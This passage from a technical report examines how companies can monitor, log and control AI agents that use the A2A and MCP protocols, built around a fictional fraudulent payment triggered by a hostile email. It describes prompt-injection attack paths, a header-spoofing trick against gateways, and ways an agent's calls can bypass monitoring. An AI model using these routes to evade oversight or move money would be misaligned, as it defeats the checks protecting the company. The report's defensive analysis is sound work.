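These findings come from an analysis of the text of A2A 1.0, not from attacks on running systems. Lotfi and colleagues used language models to turn the specification into 929 formal statements and then into a map of the protocol with 37 states and 76 transitions. They searched for harmful message sequences that remain possible when every party follows every rule and turns on every optional safeguard, and found 17 candidates. An automated check rejected one, and three of the researchers then confirmed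 11, rejected four and found one duplicate.

One of the most serious flaws is that A2A defines no owner for a context, although each task belongs to the client that created it. If another customer of the supplier-check firm learned the manufacturer's context ID, it could start a task in the same context. The reply might draw on the manufacturer's earlier conversations, and the intruder's messages could affect later supplier checks. A long random ID is hard to guess, but A2A doesn't require the server to check who is using it. The list also includes update streams that continue after a client has lost access, and agents that delegate to each other in a circle until all of them are stuck.

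The researchers used formal models to check three of the flaws, including the loss of identity. In each case, the attack worked despite A2A's existing safeguards and failed once the researchers added the missing protection. This is good evidence that A2A's rules permit the attacks, but many deployments may have extra checks that block them. A2A's technical steering committee is working with the researchers on fixes.

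There is little evidence from real deployments. Neither this analysis nor the study of public cards tested attacks on a company's live A2A system, and Schifter reports failures and missing features, not attacks. A company can't yet estimate how often such an attack would succeed against its own agents.

### What opaque execution hides

Under opaque execution, the manufacturer sees only what passes between the two agents. It can refuse to send the task or to act on the artifact, but it can't block the supplier-check agent's tool calls, because those calls run on another company's systems and don't pass through the manufacturer's gateway. If that agent sends the bank details to a stranger, the manufacturer's log shows an ordinary completed task.

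Cancelling the task may come too late, and the A2A specification doesn't guarantee that a `CancelTask` request will succeed. The manufacturer has the best chance of preventing a leak if, before sending the task, it removes everything the check doesn't need.

When one company owns both agents, it can monitor what each one does. The manufacturer runs the treasury agent, so it can log and block that agent's tool calls. It still has to connect the logs from different layers, because each layer usually keeps its own, as Ghumare notes.

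A remote agent can also report some of what it did. Eon wrote an A2A extension that returns, along with the answer, the database query, the sources and their age, and any caveats. Users can use these details to check the agent's work, but a dishonest agent can invent them too.

Schifter found that some errors from remote agents never reached the assistant's model, which then answered from the information it already had. If a supplier check failed this way, the accounts-payable agent might carry on as if the account had passed. A payment rule should therefore require explicit confirmation that the account passed.

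### Proposed remedies and their costs

The easiest remedy is to delegate only to approved agents, which *From Prompt Injections to Protocol Exploits* (2025) recommended for keeping out rogue agents. The company's agents can then no longer discover new agents automatically, but few companies would want an accounts-payable agent to do that.

Verifying card signatures takes a little more work. The official development kits already include the functions, so most of the effort goes into managing keys. *A2A Protocol 1.0 at the Gateway* lists what the operator still has to decide, including which issuers to accept and what to do when a key is revoked. The agent framework described in AG2's *card signing* accepts a card if any one of its signatures is valid, so a provider can change keys without interrupting service by publishing signatures from both the old and new keys.

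Neither measure would have enforced the clerk's EUR 10,000 limit. For that, Lotfi and colleagues propose a signed token that carries the original user and the chain of agents with each request. They suggest building it on OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange, an existing standard for swapping one access token for another. By the time the request reached the finance server, the main contents of the token might look like this:

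```
{
  "sub": "clerk-114",
  "aud": "finance-server",
  "scope": "release_payment",
  "max_payment_eur": 10000,
  "act": {
    "sub": "treasury-agent",
    "act": { "sub": "ap-agent" }
  }
}
```

The first `sub` field identifies the clerk, and the `act` fields list the agents acting for her, with the most recent agent outermost. The `aud` field identifies the only server that should accept the token. The company would define `max_payment_eur` itself. The finance server could then refuse the EUR 18,400 payment even though the treasury agent's own limit is much higher.

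Inside one company, this requires an identity system that issues a new token at each step, plus changes to every agent and server that checks the token. Between companies, both sides also have to trust the same issuers and agree on what each field means. An A2A extension could carry the token, but an agent that doesn't support an optional extension should ignore it and continue, so the chain could break without anyone noticing. The researchers therefore want the token to be part of the protocol or a standard extension. They have not yet tested how well their proposals work with existing development kits.

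They would also tie each credential to a private key held by the agent that uses it, so that an agent in the middle couldn't reuse a copy. Every agent would then need its own key, and every receiving service would have to check that the agent holds it. To counter false claims about skills, they propose attestations signed by a third party. Somebody would have to test the agents and vouch for the results, and an agent could still misbehave after passing.

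*SMCP* (Hou, Wang and colleagues, 2026) proposes a broader change to MCP. Its Secure Model Context Protocol would admit only verified users, agents and tools from a trusted registry, and would require both ends of each connection to authenticate. Every operation would carry a security context with details of identity, delegation and risk, which the system would use to apply access rules and keep an audit log.

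SMCP would show the manufacturer's finance server that the treasury agent was acting for the accounts-payable agent and the clerk. But SMCP extends MCP, so the A2A request between the two agents would still have to carry the same information. Adopting SMCP would also require changes to existing clients and servers, and a registry operator that all participating companies trust. Hou and colleagues support the design with worked examples and a list matching threats to controls, which are weaker evidence than a trial in a working company.

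A delegation chain also doesn't show whether the user wanted a particular action. If the accounts-payable agent is working for the clerk and a hostile email causes it to request a EUR 9,000 payment to the wrong account, the token will still be valid and the amount will be within her limit.

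## Where security products can observe agent traffic

A security product needs a record of the call to stop that EUR 9,000 payment, or even to find it afterwards. Suppose the accounts-payable agent again calls `release_payment` itself, without a treasury agent in between. A product could observe the call through the platform that hosts the agent, on the network between the agent and the finance server, inside the software that runs the agent, or on the machines and in the code at either end. Where it observes the call affects whether the record includes the account number and whether it arrives before the money leaves.

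### A read-only connection to the agent platform

Many companies build agents on a hosted platform, such as Microsoft's Copilot Studio or Amazon Bedrock, which keeps a list of its agents and an audit log. A security product can copy both through the platform's API with read-only permission, without any change to the agent or the network. Akamai, whose Agent Security product works this way, says setup takes minutes.

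The data a security product receives depends on the platform. According to Microsoft's documentation, the Copilot Studio log event for a conversation contains the time, the user and a transcript ID, but not the transcript itself. If the accounts-payable agent ran on Copilot Studio, the event would show that the clerk had used it that morning, but an analyst would have to look elsewhere for the account number. Akamai says its product also analyses the documents an agent retrieves and the output of the agent's tools.

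Audit records can arrive late or not at all. Datadog Security Labs' *Uncovering agent logging gaps in Copilot Studio* (2026) describes a test in which researchers created an agent, changed its settings and checked the log. Only two events had appeared after 30 minutes, and no more after 24 hours, which the researchers treat as the normal maximum delay. Changes to the agent's authentication, sharing, publication and logging settings were all missing, although Microsoft's documentation said they were logged. Microsoft fixed this in October 2025, but two of the four events became unreliable again in later tests, and Microsoft said in March 2026 that it couldn't reproduce the problem. Conversations with users who haven't logged in leave no interaction event.

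Searching the log takes more time. In Topedia's *Auditing Copilot agent changes with Microsoft Purview* (2026), an administrator reports that one search of 90 days of records took 7 minutes and another took 3 hours and 20 minutes.

A read-only connection can't block a call. Akamai offers blocking only through a gateway or the platform's own safeguards. The connection is more useful before anything goes wrong, because it can show that an agent reads outside email and has permission to release payments. Akamai gives the example of a tool whose name suggests routine record cleanup but which can delete customer data.

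### A gateway in the network path

A gateway between the MCP client and the finance server receives the whole `release_payment` request, including the amount and the account, before the server does. It can refuse the request, and it also receives the response on the way back.

Microsoft's *MCP Security Gateway* (2025), a draft specification, requires the gateway to check the agent's ID, the tool name and the arguments before forwarding a call, then scan the response for hidden instructions, leaked credentials and personal data. The gateway also writes an audit entry for every decision about a call.

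DZone's *Part 2* is a walkthrough of agentgateway, an open-source proxy hosted by the Linux Foundation. It places the proxy between Goose, an AI agent on developers' laptops, and a company's MCP server. When Goose connected directly, the server accepted any call, so an intern had the same access to the audit trail as a senior engineer. The proxy requires each caller to have a valid token and a role that permits the requested tool.

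Some gateways also handle A2A. MuleSoft's *Securing Agent Interactions with Omni Gateway* describes policies that log or block sensitive information in messages between agents. The gateway can also rewrite the address in an Agent Card so other agents send tasks to the gateway instead of directly to the agent. The manufacturer could use such a gateway to remove unnecessary bank details from a supplier check before the task leaves the company.

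A gateway usually lacks information about what led to a call. The hostile email reached the agent through a local mail server, and the clerk's request never crossed the network as an MCP message. The EUR 9,000 payment therefore reaches the gateway as a well-formed request from a legitimate client. A rule could still catch it by comparing the destination account with the one on file for the supplier.

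### What a gateway can do with the routing headers

Before the July 2026 revision, every MCP operation reached the server as a web request to the same address, with the operation named only in the JSON body. A gateway had to parse every body to tell a request for the tool list from a payment. Many simpler network products can't parse bodies, so they treated all MCP traffic alike.

Model Context Protocol's *Streamable HTTP* (2026) now requires an `Mcp-Method` header on every request. Tool calls also need `Mcp-Name`, which contains the tool's name. In the payment request, the headers that describe the call might look like this:

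```
Mcp-Method: tools/call
Mcp-Name: release_payment
Mcp-Param-Currency: EUR
```

With the first two headers, an ordinary rate limiter can allow ten `release_payment` calls a minute and leave `get_invoice` unlimited. A firewall can block `release_payment` calls from a group of test machines, and a standard access log can count calls per tool. The gateway still has to decrypt the connection, because HTTPS encrypts headers as well as bodies, but it no longer has to parse the JSON to apply these rules.

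The last header comes from an optional feature. A server's developer can mark an argument in the tool's schema with `x-mcp-header`, and the client must then copy its value into a header. *A platform team's guide to MCP 7-28* (Körbächer, 2026) gives the example of a rule that limits each customer to ten database queries a minute and forbids test machines from querying one region. Such a rule used to require parsing the body, and in most cases Körbächer had seen, nobody wrote it.

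Security products usually still have to read the message body to apply rules on arguments. Few arguments will have a header, because the server's developer has to mark each one. Only text, whole numbers and true-or-false values qualify, so a payment amount with decimals would have to be sent as text or as a whole number of cents. Values inside a list don't qualify, which rules out the account numbers in a batch of payments. Model Context Protocol's *HTTP Standardization*, the proposal that introduced the headers, advises against copying sensitive values into them, because every proxy and logging system on the route can read them. That advice would probably cover a supplier's bank account, the one argument that would reveal this fraud.

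Headers also give a hostile client a new way to deceive a gateway. The client could put `get_invoice` in the header and `release_payment` in the body. A gateway that reads only headers would allow the request as a harmless lookup, and a server that reads only the body would release the payment. Any server that processes the body must therefore reject a request whose header and body don't match, with HTTP status 400 and error code -32020.

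This makes it safe to refuse a call on its headers alone, because a request with a false header would have failed anyway. Allowing a sensitive call on its headers alone is riskier, because the gateway would rely on every server behind it to make the comparison correctly. Tigera's *The New MCP Headers Are a Gift to Gateways* recommends that gateways keep parsing the body before they allow such a call. Tigera sells such a gateway, but the reasoning holds for any product. The proposal also forbids gateways and servers from treating values copied from arguments as trusted input for security decisions, because a manipulated model may have chosen them.

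Gateways can't rely on the headers in older traffic, because the November 2025 revision didn't require clients to send the `Mcp-Name` header or servers to compare it with the body. The specification recommends that gateways check the protocol version before they trust the headers, and reject requests that declare an older version. Körbächer suggests sending older traffic through a path that inspects the body if the company can't refuse it yet. He also warns that clients Base64-encode values that contain unusual characters, so a rule for the region São Paulo would never match unless the gateway decodes the value first.

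### A hook in the agent's runtime

An agent's runtime is the software that passes text to the model and carries out the calls the model generates. Some runtimes have a hook that sends each proposed call to an outside checker and waits for a response before the runtime carries out the call.

Microsoft's *Protect your environment in real-time during agent runtime* describes a hook of this kind for Copilot Studio. Microsoft Defender inspects a tool call before it runs. If the call looks suspicious, Defender blocks it, notifies the user and raises an alert for the security team. Without a separate connection to Microsoft 365, Defender still blocks calls but shows no alerts, so the clerk might learn of a refused payment before the security team does.

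For the accounts-payable agent, a hook would report `release_payment` with its amount and account before the client sent anything to the finance server. It would also report `read_email`, because the runtime handles calls to local and remote servers the same way. If the hook also includes the conversation, the checker can see that the new account number came from an email, not the clerk. A network gateway rarely has that information.

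A hook covers only agents whose runtime supports it and for which an administrator has turned it on. It observes calls when the model proposes them, so if the agent runs a script, the hook reports the command that starts the script but not necessarily each request the script then makes. The hook also cannot observe the supplier-check agent's calls, because they happen in another company's runtime.

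### Sensors on the machine and instrumentation in the code

A sensor is a program that records the processes, files and network connections on a machine. In *The next frontier in endpoint security*, Shteinberg (2026) announced a preview version of Defender that recognises more than 20 types of local agent and the MCP servers connected to them. Security staff can search the records of these agents and servers together with data on logins, files and network traffic.

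If the accounts-payable agent ran on an office computer and was a supported type, the sensor could record its process, the local mail server and a connection to the finance server. But a sensor that only records connections can't read the encrypted request, so it would miss the account number. The analyst might still see which program made the connection, and that is stronger evidence than the name `ap-agent` in a message.

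The same preview can block malicious activity as it happens, initially only for two coding agents, Claude Code and GitHub Copilot CLI. This protection monitors the agent's loop, so it works more like a runtime hook than a traditional sensor. Miller (2026), an independent analyst, describes the protected agents as a "narrow but important range" in *Find and Secure Local AI Tools with Defender for Endpoint*.

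Instrumentation is code that developers add to an agent or a server to record what it does. It can record a call to `release_payment` with all its arguments as the call runs, but it normally can't refuse the call unless a developer adds a check. Instrumentation also works for local servers, and the July revision recommends two channels for it. Local servers can write logs to standard error, a text channel that every program has, and any server can use OpenTelemetry, an open standard for exporting traces and logs.

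The revision also standardizes the names of the `_meta` fields that hold trace identifiers. According to Model Context Protocol, a trace can then follow a tool call from the agent's application through the client and the server to the systems the server calls. This gives analysts another way to group calls now that the session ID is gone, but only if every program along the route passes on the identifier and reports its own part of the trace.

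Tigera argues that an agent shouldn't write its own audit trail, since a compromised agent could leave entries out. Instrumentation in the finance server avoids this problem and covers every caller, including programs that don't use MCP. It would record the thief's account number, but not the email that supplied it.

### Finding the agents a company already has

Companies rarely know about all the agents they run. Developers build agents with scripts and scheduled jobs that no platform lists, and employees install coding assistants on their laptops. An inventory therefore has to combine several sources.

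Platform catalogues are the easiest source to collect. Microsoft says Defender's inventory of cloud agents covers those built with Copilot Studio, Microsoft Foundry, AWS Bedrock and Google's Vertex AI. Akamai also scans the disks of cloud machines for agents that don't appear in any catalogue. On employees' computers, Defender looks for supported agents and the configuration files of their MCP servers. Customers in an early-access programme can also see which devices run OpenClaw, an autonomous agent, and block common ways of running it (Microsoft, 2026).

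These methods leave gaps. Microsoft's local discovery covers only devices enrolled in Defender, and its documentation lists specific products. Akamai describes its disk scanning as a tool for cloud workloads. A script that a clerk writes on her own laptop to let a model process invoices might therefore go undetected by both. Coverage also depends on licensing, since some Defender features for Copilot Studio and Foundry agents have required an additional licence since July 2026, according to Microsoft's transition guide.

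Agent counts from different products may not match. Defender treats each combination of user, device and agent type as one agent, so it lists Claude Code in 15 project folders on one laptop as a single entry, while another product might count 15.

A useful inventory also shows what each agent can reach. Shteinberg describes a map that links an agent to its device, its user's identity, its MCP servers and the cloud resources that identity can access. In his example, a desktop assistant has no cloud permissions of its own but inherits access to storage and encryption keys from the account it uses. The manufacturer most urgently needs to know which agents can reach the finance system. Server logs can help by showing callers that aren't in any inventory.

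### Traffic that bypasses the gateway

The mail server is local, so calls to `read_email` never reach a network gateway. Only the HTTP transport copies the tool name into headers, and MCP also allows custom transports. The manufacturer could move the mail server behind the gateway or use a runtime hook. Otherwise, its gateway log will start with the payment and omit the email that caused it.

An agent may also skip MCP and call an ordinary API. Suppose the accounts-payable agent can run code and finds a key for the finance system in a configuration file. It can then send a payment request directly to that system. An MCP gateway wouldn't receive the request, and a rule that blocks `release_payment` wouldn't apply to it. The manufacturer can prevent this by keeping the key away from the agent and configuring the finance system to accept payment requests only from approved servers. The finance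 system's own log would still record any payment that got through.

Agents can also pass messages outside A2A. Two agents in the same program may exchange text in memory, and agents in different programs can use a shared file, a chat channel or a database. For example, the accounts-payable agent might write "bank details confirmed" in an invoice's comment field, which the treasury agent reads before paying the invoice. A2A monitoring would show no contact between them. An MCP log might contain the calls that wrote and read the comment, but an analyst would have to connect them.

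The table compares what each observation point could reveal about the EUR 9,000 payment.

| Observation point | What the product receives | When | Can it refuse the call? | What it misses |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Read-only platform connection | Depends on the platform; in Copilot Studio's audit log, the time, user and transcript ID | Minutes to a day later, or never | No | Agents outside the connected platforms, and often the account number |
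| Gateway | The full request, including the amount and account, and the response | Before the call runs | Yes | The local `read_email` call, direct API calls and usually the clerk's request |
| Runtime hook | The proposed call with its arguments, sometimes with the conversation | Before the call runs | Yes | Agents without the hook, and requests made by scripts they start |
| Sensor on the machine | The agent's process, its local servers and its network connections | During the call or soon after | Only for supported agents | Usually the account number, and anything on devices without the sensor |
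| Instrumentation in the code | Whatever the developer chose to record, including arguments | During the call or soon after | Only if the developer adds a check | Programs without instrumentation |

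## Turning agent logs into one common format

Many MCP servers log too little to support an investigation. The specification leaves audit requirements to developers, and the NSA found that many implementations keep no logs or record only minimal operational data. If the finance server logged only that it had answered a request at 07:42, the manufacturer couldn't tell whether the request was an invoice lookup or the EUR 9,000 payment.

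A usable record contains the time, the user, the agent, the tool or remote agent it called, the arguments, any policy decision, the outcome and an identifier that links the record to others. The NSA also recommends storing a cryptographic hash of each result where feasible. A hash is a short fingerprint that changes if the data changes, so it can later show whether a saved copy is genuine. The log should also include refused and malformed requests, because a caller may try several tools before finding one that works.

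Different products give the same information different names. Log normalisation translates their records into a shared set of fields, each with one meaning. In Sentinel, Microsoft's security monitoring service, a program called a parser converts each product's records into a shared schema. An analyst can then search for `release_payment` once, without learning every vendor's format.

### One payment in three logs

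Suppose the treasury agent again controls `release_payment`, and a hostile email has led the accounts-payable agent to request EUR 9,000 from it. The platform that hosts the accounts-payable agent logs the clerk's conversation. The treasury agent's server stores the A2A task, and the finance server logs the tool call.

The table shows how a company might combine the three records into one event. The values are invented, but real logs differ in similar ways. MEGA's MCP server documentation, *Tool Execution*, describes an event that records the tool, its parameters, a success flag and the length of the result. The software company Qlik describes one that records the tool's name, the ID of the application that requested it, how long the tool took and any error message.

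| Common field | Platform audit log | A2A task record | Finance server's log | Combined event |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Time | 07:41:52 UTC | 07:42:33 UTC | 09:42:31 local time | 07:42:31 UTC |
| User | `clerk-114` | None | None | `clerk-114`, inferred |
| Agent | "Accounts payable" | `ap-agent`, from its login | `svc-treasury` | `ap-agent`, then `treasury-agent` |
| Tool or remote agent | None | `treasury-agent` | `release_payment` | `release_payment` |
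| Arguments | None | A written request to pay the invoice | Invoice, amount and account | Invoice, amount and account |
| Policy decision | None | None | None | Not recorded |
| Outcome | None | `TASK_STATE_COMPLETED` | `success: true` | Completed |
| Correlation | Transcript `tr-5521` | Task `task-8830` and a trace ID | Request `17` and the same trace ID | The trace ID and all three original IDs |

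The combined event might look like this:

```
{
  "time": "2026-10-05T07:42:31Z",
  "user": { "id": "clerk-114", "basis": "inferred" },
  "agents": ["ap-agent", "treasury-agent"],
  "tool": "release_payment",
  "arguments": {
    "invoice_id": "INV-20433",
    "amount_eur": 9000,
    "account": "ending 4471"
  },
  "policy_decision": "not_recorded",
  "outcome": "completed",
  "trace_id": "8a1f0c6e52d94b7fa3e07d5c19b2e466",
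  "source_records": ["tr-5521", "task-8830", "finance-17"]
}
```

The parser takes the time from the finance server's log, because the payment happened on that server, and converts it to UTC. It needs a lookup table for the agents' names, since the three logs use four names for two agents. Only the finance server's log has the account number.

The user is the least certain field in the event. Only the platform log identifies the clerk, and it doesn't contain the trace ID that links the other two records. The parser matched her conversation to the task because the same agent handled both within a minute. If two clerks were using the agent at the time, the parser could easily pick the wrong one, so the event marks the user as inferred.

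None of the three systems recorded a policy decision. The parser shouldn't fill this gap with "allowed", because that would suggest the payment had been checked. If a gateway had checked it, the gateway's log would be a fourth source. The company should also keep the original records, because it couldn't correct a parser mistake without them.

### OpenTelemetry's names for agent activity

OpenTelemetry, the open standard for traces and logs, already has names for much of this information. It records each operation as a span, which has a start time, an end time and a set of named attributes. Spans that share a trace ID form a trace. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* use `invoke_agent` for a call to an agent and `execute_tool` for running a tool. A span for the payment could include these attributes:

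```
gen_ai.operation.name = execute_tool
gen_ai.tool.name      = release_payment
mcp.method.name       = tools/call
mcp.protocol.version  = 2026-07-28
```

The tool name identifies the payment, since the method name is `tools/call` for every MCP tool call. An agent framework and an MCP library may both record the same call, so the conventions recommend that the library add its attributes to an existing tool span instead of creating another. If the library creates a second span anyway, a simple count of spans will show two payments.

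These names may still change. OpenTelemetry gave the agent conventions the status "Development" in April 2026, and by June its *MCP* attribute list had moved to a separate repository for generative AI. TrueFoundry, which sells software for running AI systems, described that repository in August as still in development. OpenTelemetry also says that existing instrumentation that follows version 1.36.0 or earlier should keep using the old names until someone turns on the new ones, so two agents in the same company may use different names for the same thing.

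The June list also predates MCP's July revision. It includes `initialize` and `mcp.session.id`, which clients no longer use under the new revision. A parser should therefore store the protocol version with each record and accept events that have no session ID.

### Failed payments in successful responses

When a bank rejects the account for a payment made through MCP, the web request can still return status 200, and the JSON-RPC message can still contain a `result` instead of an `error`. Only the `isError` field inside that result shows that the payment failed. A gateway that relies only on status codes would log the payment as completed. OWASP, a non-profit that publishes security guidance, has proposed a log format, *AOS tracing with OCSF*, that avoids this by storing the response code and an `is_error` flag separately.

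If the finance server asks the clerk to confirm the payment, it returns a successful response with a `resultType` of `input_required`. The confirmed call has a new ID, so the log contains two `release_payment` requests for one payment. If an older server's response has no `resultType`, Model Context Protocol requires clients to treat it as complete, and a parser needs the same rule.

The client and server may also record different outcomes for the same call. MEGA notes that its success flag means the tool ran without an error, not that the response reached the client. If the connection breaks after the finance server releases the money, the server will log a success and the client will log a failure. An analyst with only the client's log might wrongly conclude that the supplier hasn't been paid.

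A2A tasks have a similar problem. `TASK_STATE_COMPLETED` means the treasury agent has finished its job, but its artifact could be a message explaining why the payment failed. The finance server's record is better evidence of whether the payment went through. The common format needs separate values for a completed call, a tool error, a protocol error, a request for input, a refusal and an unknown outcome. The unknown value is needed because MEGA's server writes its event only after a call ends, so a crash halfway through a payment might leave no event.

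### What OCSF offers for agents

The Open Cybersecurity Schema Framework (OCSF) is a vendor-neutral format for all kinds of security events, including logins, network connections and file changes. Recording agent activity in OCSF would let an analyst search it alongside the company's other security data. Amazon Web Services, which helped found OCSF and has an interest in promoting it, says in *OCSF Achieves ITU Support* that more than 1,280 people from 200 organisations have contributed to it.

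OCSF added specific support for AI in version 1.8.0, released on 16 March 2026. A new profile, `ai_operation`, adds two objects to an event: `ai_model` describes the model, and `message_context` describes the exchange. According to Tenzir, which makes software for processing security data, the fields of `message_context` identify the conversation, the client application and the service that handles the request. Other fields give token counts and the role of the AI, such as assistant, tool, agent or orchestrator.

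For the EUR 9,000 payment, these fields could show that an agent contacted the finance server during a particular conversation. `message_context` has no field for the account number or for a policy decision, so a product has to put both elsewhere in the event. Version 1.9.0 was in development in May 2026. lmodel's *Class*, an independent rendering of the draft, lists the same fields.

OWASP's format uses OCSF's existing API Activity class for both tool calls and delegation between agents. It puts tool arguments under `unmapped`, the part of an OCSF event for data without a standard field. Another vendor could put the same arguments there under different names, so a search for the account number would have to cover both names.

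OWASP's own examples also put the tool's name in different fields. One has `tools/call` in `api.operation` and the tool's name under `unmapped`, while another has the tool's name in `api.operation`. A rule that looks for `release_payment` in `api.operation` would miss every payment logged the first way. Both examples put the agent in `actor.user`, where an analyst would normally expect the clerk.

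In OCSF, the `agent` object describes security and monitoring software on a machine, such as a malware sensor, according to lmodel's copy of the definition. A parser that put the AI agent `treasury-agent` there would wrongly list it among the company's security tools.

Microsoft has a separate schema for agent events in Sentinel. It distinguishes the person from the agent and the calling agent from the one it calls, which suits A2A better than OWASP's examples do. But it is only at version 0.1.0, nearly all of its agent-specific fields are optional, and it has no dedicated field for tool arguments or policy decisions. The table shows where each of the three formats puts the main fields.

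| Information | OpenTelemetry | OCSF, in OWASP's examples | Microsoft's schema |
|---|---|---|---|
| User | No agent-specific field | `actor.user`, but filled with the agent | `ActorUsername` |
| Calling agent | `gen_ai.agent.id` | `actor.user` | `SrcAgentId` |
| Tool | `gen_ai.tool.name` | `api.operation` or `unmapped` | `ToolName` |
| Remote agent | Agent name on an `invoke_agent` span | `dst_endpoint` | `TargetAgentId` |
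| Arguments | In message content, off by default | `unmapped` | `EventOriginalRequestDetails` |
| Policy decision | No standard operation for a policy check | None | None |
| Outcome | `error.type` if the operation failed | `status_id`, with `is_error` under `unmapped` | `EventErrorDetails` |
| Correlation | Trace, span and conversation IDs | `correlation_uid` and trace ID | `EventSessionId` and `EventRequestId` |

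A company could combine formats by collecting spans with OpenTelemetry, which developers also use to find faults, and converting the security-relevant ones to OCSF or Microsoft's schema. AWS reports that the maintainers of OpenTelemetry and OCSF have begun working together to connect the two. Until they agree on a mapping, the company has to maintain its own and define fields for the arguments and the policy decision.

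### Linking records without a session ID

With the session ID gone, analysts can group calls by the trace context in `_meta`. The main key is `traceparent`:

```
"_meta": {
  "traceparent": "00-8a1f0c6e52d94b7fa3e07d5c19b2e466-5be1d07f3c92a648-01"
}
```

The value has four parts, separated by hyphens: the format version, the trace ID, the ID of the span that made the call, and a flag indicating whether the caller is recording the trace. The finance server creates a new span with the same trace ID and records the caller's span as its parent.

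Trace context travels in the message body, so it also works for local servers that don't use HTTP headers. pkg.go.dev's *mcp* (2026), the documentation for a package that adds OpenTelemetry to MCP programs, describes how trace context joins the client's and server's spans into one trace. The revision also defines `tracestate`, which holds data for particular tracing products, and `baggage`, which developers can use to pass details such as an invoice number. Every server that receives the message can read the baggage, so it shouldn't contain bank details.

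Other identifiers are poor substitutes. The JSON-RPC `id` only matches a response to its request, and two clients could both use ID 17. The `mcpCorrelationId` field in MEGA's log identifies the caller, so searching for one value could return many unrelated calls. A conversation ID is more useful, but OpenTelemetry calls for it only when the instrumentation has one available.

A trace ID links events but doesn't prove who caused them. The caller supplies the ID, and MCP doesn't stop a program from sending one that belongs to someone else's work. A fraudulent payment could then appear in the log as part of the clerk's legitimate session. The finance server should take the caller's identity from a verified token and store it in a field that the caller can't set. The server, not the caller, should also control which calls are recorded, because many tracing systems follow the caller's recording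 flag by default.

A2A agents don't have to expose their internal workings to each other, so a company's traces usually end where another company's agent takes over. In a supplier check, the A2A task ID is often the last link in the manufacturer's trace.

### MCP's own log messages

MCP has a Logging feature that sends a server's log messages to the client. It still works, but the July revision deprecates it in favour of standard error and OpenTelemetry, so new software shouldn't adopt it.

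MCP's built-in logging was never well suited to an audit trail. The messages go to the client, which is one of the programs the security team wants to check. Under the new revision, a server can send them only if the client's request sets a log level, so the client can prevent them by leaving it out. Logging to standard error doesn't depend on the request, but the output is plain text without a fixed format. Each local server may need its own parser, and the company has to collect the text from every machine.

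### Sensitive data and redaction

Exact arguments are useful to an investigator but risky to store. A log of `release_payment` calls contains suppliers' bank accounts, and a log of `read_email` results contains whatever people write to the company. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* warn that message content is likely to include personal data, and leave it out by default. If a company keeps this default, its traces may lack the one field that would reveal the fraud.

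Removing the account number protects the supplier but prevents anyone from comparing it with the account on file. The example above keeps the last four digits, which help an analyst recognise an account but can't prove a match. A better compromise is for the finance server to store a keyed hash, which it computes from the full number and a secret key. The same account always produces the same hash, so a monitoring system can check whether the payment went to the supplier's usual account without access to the number.

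A hash without a key would be weaker, because account numbers follow a known format and someone with the log could try likely numbers until one matched. The key has to stay outside the log system, because someone who had both could do the same. The server also has to remove spaces and put account numbers in a consistent format before hashing, or one account written two ways will look like two accounts.

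Passwords and access tokens have no comparable use in an investigation, so the server should delete them before the record leaves the machine. Investigators need the text of the hostile email to explain why the agent requested the payment, but most analysts don't. The manufacturer could keep full messages in a separate store that fewer people can read, with a shorter retention period, and put only a reference to them in the common event.

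### Storage volume

The database company Greptime (2026) explains that a call to a language model produces far more data than an ordinary web request. Prompts and responses are long, and each tool's arguments have their own structure. Agents add to the volume by resending the conversation so far to the model at every step, including the emails they have already read.

Suppose an agent processes an invoice in ten steps, each adding 5 KB of text. Saving only the new text takes 50 KB. Saving the full input at every step takes 275 KB, because the log repeats earlier text and stores the first email ten times. For three hundred invoices a night, the totals are 15 MB and 82.5 MB, both easy to store. But the repeated text grows roughly with the square of the number of steps. For a coding agent that takes fifty 5 KB steps, saving full inputs would take about 6.4 MB per job, compared with 250 KB for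 only the new text.

Engineers often reduce the cost of tracing by keeping only a sample of traces. This works for measuring speed, but if the manufacturer kept one trace in ten at random, it would have a 90 per cent chance of losing the record of any particular payment. It makes more sense to keep every tool call as a small structured record and save money by storing less of the surrounding text. MEGA's event, for example, records only the length of a result, which takes little space but doesn't show what the agent read. A hash of the result takes little more space and lets an investigator check whether a copy from another source matches.

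AWS says that storing OCSF data in a columnar format such as Parquet reduces storage and search costs, though it gives no figures. Columnar formats store each field's values together, so a search for tool names doesn't have to read the arguments. They will help less with long, varied text than with short fields whose values repeat.

### Clock differences

The three logs in the example come from three machines, whose clocks may disagree. If the finance server's clock were a minute slow, the payment would appear to happen before the clerk's conversation. Converting local times to UTC doesn't fix this, because a wrong local time converts to a wrong UTC time.

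A company can synchronise its own clocks but not another firm's. The central log system should therefore add the time it received each record and keep the original time. A large gap between the two times may mean that a clock is wrong or that the record was delayed. Trace context gives better evidence of order because a parent span has to start before any call made within it, but it can't order two calls that run in parallel.

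Some records also cover more than one event. Qlik publishes a summary after a set number of tool calls (five by default) or after a timeout. The summary refers to the events for the individual calls, so a parser should build the timeline from those events. If it treated the summary as another call, both the order and the count would be wrong.

### Protecting records from tampering

An attacker who controls the finance server could delete the payment from its log. The server should therefore send each record immediately to a store where it can add entries but not change or remove them. Records from before the break-in would then survive, although the attacker could still send false ones afterwards.

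A hash chain makes changes to records easier to detect. Each record includes the hash of the previous one, so deleting or editing an entry breaks the link to the next. Someone who controls the whole store could still change a record and recalculate every later hash, and removing the newest records would leave no broken link. The company can guard against both by regularly saving the latest hash in a different system.

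The NSA also recommends signing MCP messages, because the protocol doesn't check their integrity and relies on encrypting the connection. A signature inside the JSON would let an investigator verify the account number in a stored request, if the log kept the signed message unchanged. Redacting the number would break the signature, so the signed original would have to go into the restricted store. The NSA also suggests adding an expiry time and replay protection, which would help a server reject an old payment request that someone resends.

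A valid signature shows which key signed a message, but a compromised program can sign false information with its own key. Runtime attestation partly addresses this problem by providing evidence of which software was running. *Linux Foundation to Govern TRACE, an Open Standard for AI Runtime Attestation* (Kovacs, 2026) reported in August that AMD, Intel, Microsoft, OPAQUE and TII had developed a shared standard for such evidence in agent deployments. Attestation could help the manufacturer detect a modified treasury agent, but it wouldn't flag the EUR 9,000 payment, because unmodified software made that call after the accounts-payable agent read a hostile email.

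## How a policy decides whether a call is allowed

To stop the EUR 9,000 payment, the manufacturer needs a policy that forbids it and software that applies the policy before the finance server runs the call. Security engineers split this job between two components. The policy decision point compares a proposed call with the policy and decides whether to allow it. The policy enforcement point holds the call until it receives the decision, then forwards or refuses the call.

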